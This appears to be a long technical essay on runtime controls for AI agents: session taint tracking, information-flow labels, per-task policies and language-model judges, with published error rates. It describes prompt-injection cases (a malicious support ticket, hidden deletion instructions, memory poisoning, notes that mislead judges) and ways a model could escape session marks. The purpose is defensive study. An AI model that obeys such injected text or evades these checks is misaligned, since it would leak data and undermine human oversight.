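A filter without memory is most likely to succeed at the third call. It could search the data for email addresses, but the agent might have compressed the list first, or the call might contain only the name of a file to upload. The filter could also permit only listed destinations. That would work, but it would also block every legitimate site not yet listed.

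A milter rarely has this problem, because it can check the whole message before the server accepts it. If the message contains the customer list, the milter can detect it without a record of where the sender got it. A sender can still evade the check by encrypting the list or splitting it across fifty short messages. But prohibited content usually arrives in a single message, whereas an agent's harmful action may be spread over several calls, some of which have already run.

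*Autonomous Action Runtime Management (AARM)* (2026), a specification for agent filters, has a separate category for actions that the policy permits but whose acceptability depends on what else has happened in the session, so the filter must keep a record of the session to judge them.

### Rules that remember

Amazon's agent gateway can apply such rules. AWS's *Policy sessions and identity propagation* gives several examples. A rule can limit how many times an agent does something, such as three bank transfers per session. It can require an order, such as running the tests before deploying software. It can also forbid a combination of actions, so that an agent that has opened a patient's chart may not call any outside service for the rest of the session.

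A rule that counts calls must specify whether to include those that time out. *Agenra* counts every attempt it has permitted, even if the outcome is unknown, which is the safer choice for payments.

A rule can also compare values. In another example from AWS, an agent may transfer money only to an account that a balance lookup returned within the past hour. This stops transfers to account numbers the model has made up. If the lookup tool accepts any account, an attacker may still get around the rule by getting the agent to look up the attacker's account first.

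The usual rule against prompt injection marks the session once the agent has read untrusted material, and then refuses certain actions. Researchers call such a session "tainted". The rule needs only two states:

```text
A new session starts CLEAN.

Before a tool call:
    if the session is MARKED and the action is restricted:
        refuse the call
    otherwise:
        go on to the other checks

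After a tool call, before the model reads the result:
    if the result comes from an untrusted source,
    or from a saved note labelled MARKED:
        set the session to MARKED

When the agent saves a note for later sessions:
    label the note with the session's current state

A MARKED session never becomes CLEAN again.
```

The last line is necessary because the untrusted text stays in the model's context and could influence any later call. *SPIDES* (2026), a system for agents that use a web browser, also only tightens its labels, but it asks the user for approval when this algorithm would refuse.

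The labels on saved notes guard against attacks that span two sessions. In *Trojan Hippo Bench* (2026), an agent reads a malicious message and stores the attacker's instructions in its long-term memory. It retrieves them in a later session while working on a harmless task. With permanent labels, retrieving the note marks the second session too, and the paper proves that the attack then can't succeed. An agent with a shell would need labels on ordinary files as well, since it can save a web page in a project folder in one session and read it in a later one.

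In Claude Code, a `PostToolUse` hook could set the mark in time. Failed calls need a marking hook too, since an error page can contain an injection. Marking hooks need more careful failure handling than an ordinary check, which leaves only one call unchecked if it crashes and fails open. If a marking hook fails open, the session stays unmarked and every later restriction that depends on the mark is lost.

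### Choosing what to mark

This algorithm would not stop the three-step example. The configuration file and the database both belong to the company, so the session would still be clean when the agent sent the data out. The filter needs a second mark for sessions that have read private data.

Omnigent, a system from Databricks, keeps one mark for untrusted content and another for private data. *Innocent until combined* (Sinha, Pamulapati and Khawaja) describes a support agent that reads a customer's ticket, looks up what it needs and replies by email. An attacker's ticket tells the agent to fetch the company's quarterly revenue and send a copy to an outside address. Reading the ticket sets the first mark, and reading the revenue document sets the second. With both marks set, the policy refuses the email. When another customer asks for a password-reset link, the agent never opens a private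 document, so the policy allows its reply.

Sinha and colleagues demonstrate their own company's product on a few cases and report no error rates. Their rule would let the three-step example through, because it refuses outgoing data only if both marks are set. AWS's rule for patient records would stop it, because private data alone is enough for a refusal. But a support agent under that rule couldn't write to a customer after looking up that customer's account.

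People also have to classify the sources correctly. In Omnigent they do this in the agent's configuration, which the agent can't change while it runs. *Agenra* warns that a trusted retrieval tool can still return text an attacker wrote. For example, a company's ticket database is internal, but customers write the tickets.

### What marking costs

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025), by Costa, Köpf and colleagues at Microsoft, measured how much work an agent can still do under such rules. The tests used AgentDojo, a set of 97 tasks in four simulated settings, with attacks planted in the material the agent reads. The rules blocked important actions, such as payments, if untrusted text could have influenced them, and restricted who could receive confidential data.

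The agents in this table used OpenAI's GPT-4o:

| Agent | Successful attacks | Workspace tasks done | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic agent, no rules | 152 | 75% | 70% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Basic agent with rules | 0 | 37% | 73% | 37.5% | 20% |
| FIDES with rules | 0 | 59% | 41% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

The rules stopped every attack, excluding a few cases that AgentDojo scored as successful attacks but the researchers, after inspecting them, did not. However, the basic agent's average completion rate across the four settings fell from 84% to 42%. Many banking tasks ask the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, for example to pay a bill. Reading the file marks the session, so the rules block the payment whether the user wants the bill paid or an attacker planted it.

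FIDES, the researchers' own system, recovers some of this loss by labelling each piece of data and keeping untrusted text away from the model. When the agent fetches emails, the harness stores the text and gives the model only a name for it, such as `#read_emails_0`. The model can then write a call that sends `#read_emails_0` to the user on Slack, and the harness inserts the text. Since the model hasn't read the emails, they can't have influenced its choice of action.

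If the task requires a summary, FIDES passes the text to a second model that has no tools. An attacker could still spoil the summary but couldn't use it to start a payment. The design also lets the main model receive a yes-or-no answer, such as whether an email contains a meeting request. Such an answer has little room for an injection, so a policy could accept it, although the tested version didn't limit answers this way.

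Labels can also list who may read the data. If Dana, Lee and Sam may read one document, and Lee, Sam and Kim may read another, then a text based on both may go only to Lee and Sam. In the three-step example, the customer list's label would limit readers to company staff, so the web request would fail even though the agent had read nothing untrusted. An agent can still leak a little information through which tools it calls, and the labels don't cover that.

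FIDES completed 50% of tasks on average, still far fewer than the unrestricted agent. Some failures occurred because GPT-4o confused the names of stored data, and OpenAI's o1 did better. Current models would probably make fewer such mistakes, but no model can complete a task that the rules forbid. The survey *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (2026) adds that methods like this one slow the agent down considerably.

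### Refusing fewer actions

A less disruptive approach is to mark sessions just as readily but refuse fewer actions in them. Workloft, a small firm, tried this on its own agents. In *Read the web, lose the shell*, Alfred and Bob (2026) describe hooks that mark a Claude Code session after it reads something from the open web. The hooks then refuse a short list of actions, including reading files of passwords, uploading to unknown sites, and downloading and running a program.

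Workloft tested the hooks by replaying recorded calls without running them. The existing hooks alone had blocked 6 of 32 injected calls, and adding the new ones raised that to 31. The one missed call hid data in a web page's address. The new hooks blocked none of 50 real calls from marked sessions.

Those 50 calls are too few to show that false alarms are rare. In the full set of 8,166 real calls from 66 sessions, the hooks would have blocked 80, which is just under 1% of calls but more than one per session. Most of the 80 were genuine uploads. Workloft had also adjusted the rules using these same recordings, so new work may well produce more false alarms. The session had already read something untrusted before 72% of the real calls, so a rule that refused every important action in a marked session would have applied to most of the firm's work.

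Workloft modelled its policy file on AgenticRei, a policy system for company agents. *Deontic Policies for Runtime Governance of Agentic AI Systems* (2026) describes the system's permissions, prohibitions, obligations and dispensations (releases from an obligation). A rule can cover a class, so a ban on sharing health data applies to any kind of record the company later adds to that class. Administrators can also give a project's permission priority over a company-wide prohibition. Claude Code doesn't allow this, because its deny rules always take precedence. Such priorities make exceptions easier, but a badly chosen one could cancel a prohibition that other people rely on.

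### Rules for a single task

A rule can be much stricter if its author knows what the user asked for. Sapien, a system from Google, has a language model write a new policy for each task before the agent reads anything. *Sapien* (Tiffany, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) uses the request "Pay my Acme invoice" as an example. The policy requires the agent to read the list of invoices first, and then permits a payment only to Acme and only for the amount on the invoice. Ordinary code enforces most of this and tracks the agent's progress.

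The result resembles the fixed order of commands that SMTP uses for all mail, but Sapien needs a new order for every request.

To test the policies, Tiffany and colleagues assumed that an attacker controlled the agent completely and looked for any permitted series of calls that would achieve the attacker's goal. On AgentDojo, Sapien ruled out 93–95% of 949 attacks, depending on the model, compared with 83–87% for a simple list of permitted tools. Agents completed one to five fewer of the 97 tasks than they did without a policy.

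Sapien did less well on Toolathlon, a set of longer tasks with over 600 tools, where it ruled out 65% of 212 attacks, compared with 32% for the list of tools. The attacks used the same tools and data as the tasks themselves. In one, the agent had to compile interview feedback, and the attacker wanted it to change a rejection to a "strong hire". A rule about which file the agent may write would not prevent that change.

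The results don't show that Sapien is less secure than FIDES, because Costa and colleagues counted attacks that worked on a real model, while this test counted every attack possible for an agent fully under an attacker's control. Sapien does seem to preserve far more of the agent's usefulness.

Its main drawback is that only the enforcement is fixed. The same request may produce a different policy the next time, so a company can't test the policy in advance the way it could test a rule it wrote itself. The model also writes the policy without access to the data. In one test it wrote a rule for "London Luxury Hotel", but the name in the database was "London Luxury", so the agent could not finish the task.

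### Who keeps the memory

The milter library gives a filter one private record per connection for storing state. The record lasts only until the client disconnects, so a filter that limits an account to 100 messages a day needs its own database. Otherwise, an agent could reset the count by reconnecting.

MCP used to have sessions, identified by the `Mcp-Session-Id` header, but the July 2026 version removed them. Model Context Protocol (2026) attributes the change to the work sessions created for operators running several copies of a server, who needed a shared store of session data and had to send each client back to the same copy. Now any copy can answer any request, but the Agentic AI Foundation explains that each request must include whatever context the server needs.

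A server that has to connect several calls can issue a handle, such as `basket-17`, which the model passes back as an ordinary argument. This works for a shopping basket but not for a security mark, because a model under an attacker's influence could omit the handle or use one from a clean session.

MCP also lets a server give the client data to return later, for example after the user has answered a question. Model Context Protocol's *request_state* notes that the server must treat the returned data as attacker-controlled, so the Python library seals it and checks the seal. The seal reveals changes but doesn't by itself prevent a client from returning an older copy from before the session was marked.

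The interceptor proposal reserves a place for state shared between interceptors but does not define how it would work. Whoever sets up the filter therefore has to decide where to store the marks.

The harness is one place to keep the marks. It tracks which session a call belongs to, and its hooks can cover local tools as well as remote ones. When a user resumes an old session, the harness has to restore the mark along with the text. But if the hook keeps its marks in a file on the same machine, an agent with shell access might edit it.

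Posta argues for a trusted component outside the agent, such as a gateway. Posta was writing on a gateway project's blog, but the argument is sound because the agent can't alter a record it can't reach. However, if the agent in the three-step example read the file and queried the database with local tools, the gateway would receive only the web request.

Amazon's gateway stores the session history, but the application chooses the session identifier, and a new identifier starts an empty history. An agent whose code could set the header containing that identifier could escape restrictions triggered by its earlier actions. The gateway ties each session to the caller's login, so one user's actions don't count against another's. AWS recommends a new session for each conversation, so a limit of three transfers resets with each one. Using a single session per user prevents that reset, but then opening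 a patient's chart for one task blocks outside calls in unrelated tasks. The history expires only after 24 hours without activity.

The safest arrangement probably combines hooks in the harness with a service on another machine. The hooks would report what the agent reads, and the service would store the marks and answer queries from both the hooks and the gateway. The harness would supply the session identifier, and the model could not change it.

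Even a rule that covers a whole session can fail when several agents work together. One agent might read the customer list and write a summary, and a second might send the summary to an outside address. If each agent has its own session, the second session has no record that the list was read. Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues (*Policy Compiler for Secure Agentic Systems*, 2026) argue that a simple list of messages can't capture such flows. Their system keeps a graph of what each step depended on, so a rule can trace the outgoing summary back to the customer list, whichever agent read it.

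## A language model as the judge inside the filter

A fixed rule that checks only an agent's proposed call can't distinguish a user's request from an attack when both produce the same call. For example, an agent might propose to delete the drafts in a folder called Forecasts because the user asked it to clear out old drafts, or because it followed hidden text in a document. The arguments are the same in both cases, but only the second is an attack.

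Company policies leave a similar gap. An employee understands "don't share unreleased results outside the company", but no search pattern can reliably recognise unreleased results in an email. Some filters therefore use a judge model, which can read the request and the policy along with the proposed call.

### Google's semantic governance policies

According to Faisal's *Google Adds a Safety Check That Reads Every AI Agent Action* (2026), Google released a preview of a judge of this kind, called semantic governance policies, on 20 November 2026. UMass Amherst's *Bagdasarian's Contextual Agent Security Adopted in Google Cloud Gemini Enterprise* credits the design to Eugene Bagdasarian, a professor there, and Lillian Tsai.

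A company writes its rules in plain English and applies each one to a single tool or to all of an agent's tools. Google Cloud's *Semantic governance overview* describes how the check then works:

1. The agent's model replies with a proposed tool call, and Google's Agent Gateway intercepts the reply before it reaches the agent.
2. The gateway looks up the policies for that agent and sends them to the judge with the proposed call, the user's prompt, the earlier conversation and the list of tools. The judge also reads the agent's system instructions.
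3. The judge applies two tests: whether the call matches what the user asked for, and whether it complies with the policies. The call must pass both.
4. If it passes, the reply goes to the agent unchanged. If it fails, a denial message replaces the reply, including the tool call.
5. The system logs the verdict, the judge's reason and the amount of text the judge processed.

The first test is on by default and works even if the company has written no policies. The denial message normally includes the judge's reason, but the company can supply its own wording.

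This check comes earlier than a `PreToolUse` hook, because the harness never receives a refused call. Since the gateway reads the model's reply, it should be able to check calls to local tools as well as remote ones. The gateway can't check what a script does once it is running.

### The finance agent's three calls

*Google's semantic governance policies can block an AI agent's tool call* (Pogorelec, 2026) describes Google's example of an agent for a finance team. The agent can look through a shared drive, open files, send email and delete drafts. The company has given it a single policy: until the earnings release, it may send unreleased quarterly results only to addresses at example.com, even if the request is urgent, comes from a senior person or involves someone who has signed a confidentiality agreement.

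In the first case, an employee asks the agent to email the preliminary results to the company's controller. The call passes both tests.

In the second, the agent tries to send the results to an outside investor, with a copy to the employee's personal Gmail address. The policy forbids this even though the employee asked for it. The judge denies the whole email, not just the Gmail copy.

In the third, the agent reads a planning document with hidden instructions to delete the drafts in the Forecasts folder. The policy covers only the results, so the intent test has to catch this call. It does, because the user never asked for the deletion.

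A fixed rule could have stopped the second email, but only by refusing all mail to that investor, including an invitation to the earnings call. The judge can allow the invitation because it considers the content. But it also needs to know the release date, which Google advises companies to put in the agent's system instructions. If the company postponed the release and nobody updated the instructions, the judge might let the results out early.

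### Google's stated limits

Deepti Sehrawat, the Google engineer who announced the feature, warns that verdicts may vary because a language model produces them. Sehrawat recommends starting with a dry run, in which the judge logs its verdicts but blocks nothing, similar to audit mode for interceptors.

The judge doesn't check streamed responses, which a model sends piece by piece as it writes them. According to Google Cloud's *Configure semantic governance policies*, streaming produces either no verdict or an error, so a company has to turn it off for its agents. The judge also doesn't check replies without tool calls. If an outsider could chat with the finance agent, the agent could reveal the results in such a reply.

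The three cases illustrate the design but don't measure how often it works. Google has promised to test it on AgentDojo in a later post.

### How often judges are wrong

The judge in Claude Code's auto mode approves or blocks actions in place of the user, and Anthropic has published its error rates. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes two stages. The first gives a quick yes or no and leans towards blocking. The second reviews only the calls that the first flagged, and reasons before deciding.

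| Test set | Error measured | First stage only | Both stages |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10,000 real tool calls by Anthropic staff | Harmless calls blocked | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| 52 real calls that went beyond what the user wanted | Harmful calls missed | 6.6% | 17% |
| 1,000 artificial attempts to send data out | Harmful calls missed | 1.8% | 5.7% |

The second stage removes most of the false alarms but also lets more harmful calls through. The 17% miss rate is the most relevant to everyday work, but it comes from only 52 cases, so the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 9% to 30%. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the judge identified the danger but misclassified the action as one the user had agreed to. For example, a user who says "clean up the PR" (a proposed code change) has not agreed to overwrite the project's history.

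*Measuring the Permission Gate* (Ji, Li and colleagues, 2026) independently tested this weakness with 128 requests that made the user's aim clear but left the permitted scope or risk vague. Agents working on these requests took 253 actions that changed something. Auto mode missed 81% of the harmful ones, partly because it lets agents edit files inside the project without consulting the judge. Among the 160 actions that the judge did review, it still missed 70.3% of the harmful ones and blocked 31.9% of the harmless ones.

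Ji and colleagues chose hard cases on purpose, so they don't think their result contradicts Anthropic's. It does show that a judge's error rate depends heavily on how clearly users write their requests. Anthropic has also changed the judge since that test in April. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that the miss rate on artificial attacks by the safety company Apollo Research fell from 12% to 7% after improvements, some of which gave the judge more information about the code repository.

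A judge that rarely misses an attack may also block most harmless requests. Ray (2026), in *What Can Be Enforced?*, tested 23 judges on 97 ordinary requests and 35 attackers' goals from AgentDojo. At a cautious setting, the judge Gemma-2-9B missed only 1% of the attackers' goals but blocked 78% of the ordinary requests. The test used bare instructions without the context a real filter would have, so the figures may be too pessimistic. None of the other 22 judges was clearly better than Gemma-2-9B, and larger models didn't consistently outperform smaller ones.

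Ray also put two small judges in front of a working agent for 949 runs each. One cut successful attacks from 4.7% to 0.4%, but it blocked 78% of all calls, and the agent's task success fell from 25% to 18%. The other blocked 12% of calls and cut successful attacks only to 3.2%, a drop that could be due to chance.

### Ten harmful calls in 10,000

If harmful calls are rare, most of the calls that even a fairly accurate judge blocks will be harmless. Suppose an agent makes 10,000 calls, of which 10 are harmful, and the judge misses 10% of harmful calls and wrongly blocks 1% of harmless ones. It blocks 9 harmful calls and about 100 harmless ones, so only about 8% of the calls it blocks are harmful.

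The table applies Anthropic's figures to the same 10,000 calls, using the miss rates from the 52 real cases.

| Judge | Harmful calls stopped | Harmless calls blocked | Share of blocked calls that were harmful |
|---|---|---|---|
| Misses 10%, wrongly blocks 1% | 9 | 100 | 8% |
| Auto mode, first stage only | 9 | 849 | 1% |
| Auto mode, both stages | 8 | 40 | 17% |

In this example, the second stage prevents about 800 false alarms but lets through one more harmful call. It is therefore worth using if each false alarm causes serious problems. If a single harmful call could destroy a production database, a company might reasonably prefer the first stage alone.

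If every blocked call were sent to a person, the person in the first example would see about 11 harmless calls for each harmful one and might soon approve them all by habit. Anthropic hired 1,053 testers for a coding task and replaced one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of the testers refused it, while auto mode blocked 89% of the same commands. Among testers who had already answered 50 or more prompts, about 5% refused. The testers weren't working on their own projects, so they may have been less careful than usual, but it seems unwise to rely on people who have to answer many prompts.

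Claude Code instead returns the refusal to the agent, which can look for a safer way to do the task. After a false alarm, the agent usually has to retry once. After three refusals in a row, or 20 in a session, Claude Code asks the user what to do, or ends the run if no user is there. With the first stage alone, a task with 200 calls would have about 17 false alarms and often come close to the limit of 20.

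Retries also give a harmful action more chances to get through. Ray gives a formula for the simplest case, in which every attempt is harmful and the judge's errors are independent. If the judge misses a share *m* of harmful calls, the chance that at least one of *n* attempts gets through is 1 − (1 − *m*)ⁿ. With a 10% miss rate and three attempts, the chance is about 27%. Real errors are not independent, because a judge that refuses a call once will probably refuse it again. But an agent can change the call between attempts, so the limit on refusals matters for safety as well as convenience.

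### Why the same errors cost less in spam filtering

Spam filters also rely on statistical judgement and make both kinds of mistake. Their task is easier in one respect because spam is common. If half of 10,000 messages are spam, a filter with the same error rates catches 4,500 of them and wrongly flags 50 genuine messages, so about 99% of what it flags is spam.

Mistakes also do less harm in mail filtering than in checking agent actions. A doubtful message can wait in a junk folder, where the recipient can find it later, but holding a doubtful tool call usually holds up the agent's whole session. Letting a spam message through wastes a few seconds, whereas files deleted because the filter allowed a bad call may be lost permanently.

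Spam filters also have far more examples to learn from, because people report spam every day. A real harmful call becomes a test case only if an agent attempts one and someone notices and records it, which is why Anthropic had only 52 such cases.

Limiting what the judge can do is one way to make false alarms less disruptive. *AgentTrust* (2026) describes a system that combines rules with a model. It can respond to a doubtful action with a warning or a review, but is designed never to block a harmless action outright. This suits an agent whose user is nearby. In an unattended run, a review has the same effect as a block because nobody is there to carry it out.

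### Text that misleads the judge

A judge that reads the same untrusted text as the agent may fall for the same prompt injection. Ray inserted a short note into the text the judges read, with the claim that an administrator had already approved the action. Eight of the 11 judges tested this way then missed a larger share of harmful requests, by 20 to 60 percentage points. The conversation that Google's judge reads could well include documents with such notes.

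Anthropic's main answer is to hide that text from the judge. In auto mode, the judge receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the results of those calls. If the agent follows an instruction on a web page to send a file of passwords to some address, the judge doesn't see the page, but it has enough grounds to refuse because the call would send passwords to an address the user didn't mention.

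Anthropic also removes what Claude writes about its own actions, because an agent could argue that a dangerous command is safe or that the user has already approved it. Including Claude's messages and the tool results made the judge worse at catching actions that went too far. A version that read only the tool calls missed fewer of these actions, but it blocked some that the user had clearly requested.

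The judge does lose useful information this way. If the agent cancels job "abc123" and the user never gave that name, the judge can't tell whether the agent found it in a list of the user's jobs or made it up. This is less of a problem for a mail filter, because the server can supply facts such as the login name separately from the sender's text. Auto mode now does something similar by giving the judge the repository's status before a command that could discard unsaved work. *Shall We Approve?* (2026) tests an approver called CAPER that also receives a report of the command's effects, and the harness undoes the command if CAPER refuses it. The harness can undo changes to files, but not the sending of an email.

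Hiding tool results doesn't help if untrusted text arrives as a user message. *Ajar* (2026) found that auto mode allowed every tested call when the instruction came from the user. Allowing such calls is often correct, since users are permitted to ask for risky things, but a user can also paste in an email without noticing the instructions inside it. Subagents create a similar problem because they receive the main agent's instructions as though a user had written them. Auto mode therefore checks the task before the main agent hands it over and reviews the subagent's actions when the subagent finishes.

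Anthropic commissioned a test of 720 prompt injection attempts against Claude models in auto mode, and none succeeded. This is weak evidence for the judge, because only 0.09% succeeded on average even without auto mode. The results for OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol are better evidence of a reviewer's effect, because attacks succeeded 19% of the time with full access and 5.8% with Codex's own automatic reviewer.

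Willison (2026) wanted more independent confirmation of the zero. Crosley reports in *Claude Code Auto Mode Is Not a Security Boundary* that later that month the security researcher Johann Rehberger published an attack that worked against Claude Opus 5 in auto mode in three of five runs. Five runs are too few to estimate a success rate, but the three successes show that the defence can fail.

### Fixed rules around the judge

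A judge can be wrong or misled, and the harm from a mistaken approval depends on what the approval allows. In Google's design, the agent's ordinary permissions still apply, so an approval can't give the agent access it didn't already have. A misled judge therefore leaves the company no worse protected than having no judge. In auto mode, the judge decides on calls that the user would otherwise be asked to approve, so a mistaken approval can let through a call that a careful user would have refused.

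Claude Code limits this risk by applying the user's deny rules before the judge. It also suspends very broad allow rules, such as one for every Python command, which would otherwise let the most dangerous calls skip the judge. Anthropic has since added "hard denies", which are categories of action, such as sending secrets to outside parties, that the judge should refuse even if the user asks. Hard denies still depend on the judge to classify the command correctly, whereas a firewall that blocks unknown addresses does not.

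Google also combines trained and fixed defences in Workspace, its office software. The fixed ones include asking the user to confirm an action, sanitising URLs and restricting which tools can follow one another. Google can update these by changing a setting, so they are useful against a new attack while Google retrains a model.

Some policies need no judge. One of Google's sample policies allows refunds only up to $80, which a fixed rule can check from the amount in the tool call. The judge is more useful for deciding whether the customer asked for a refund.
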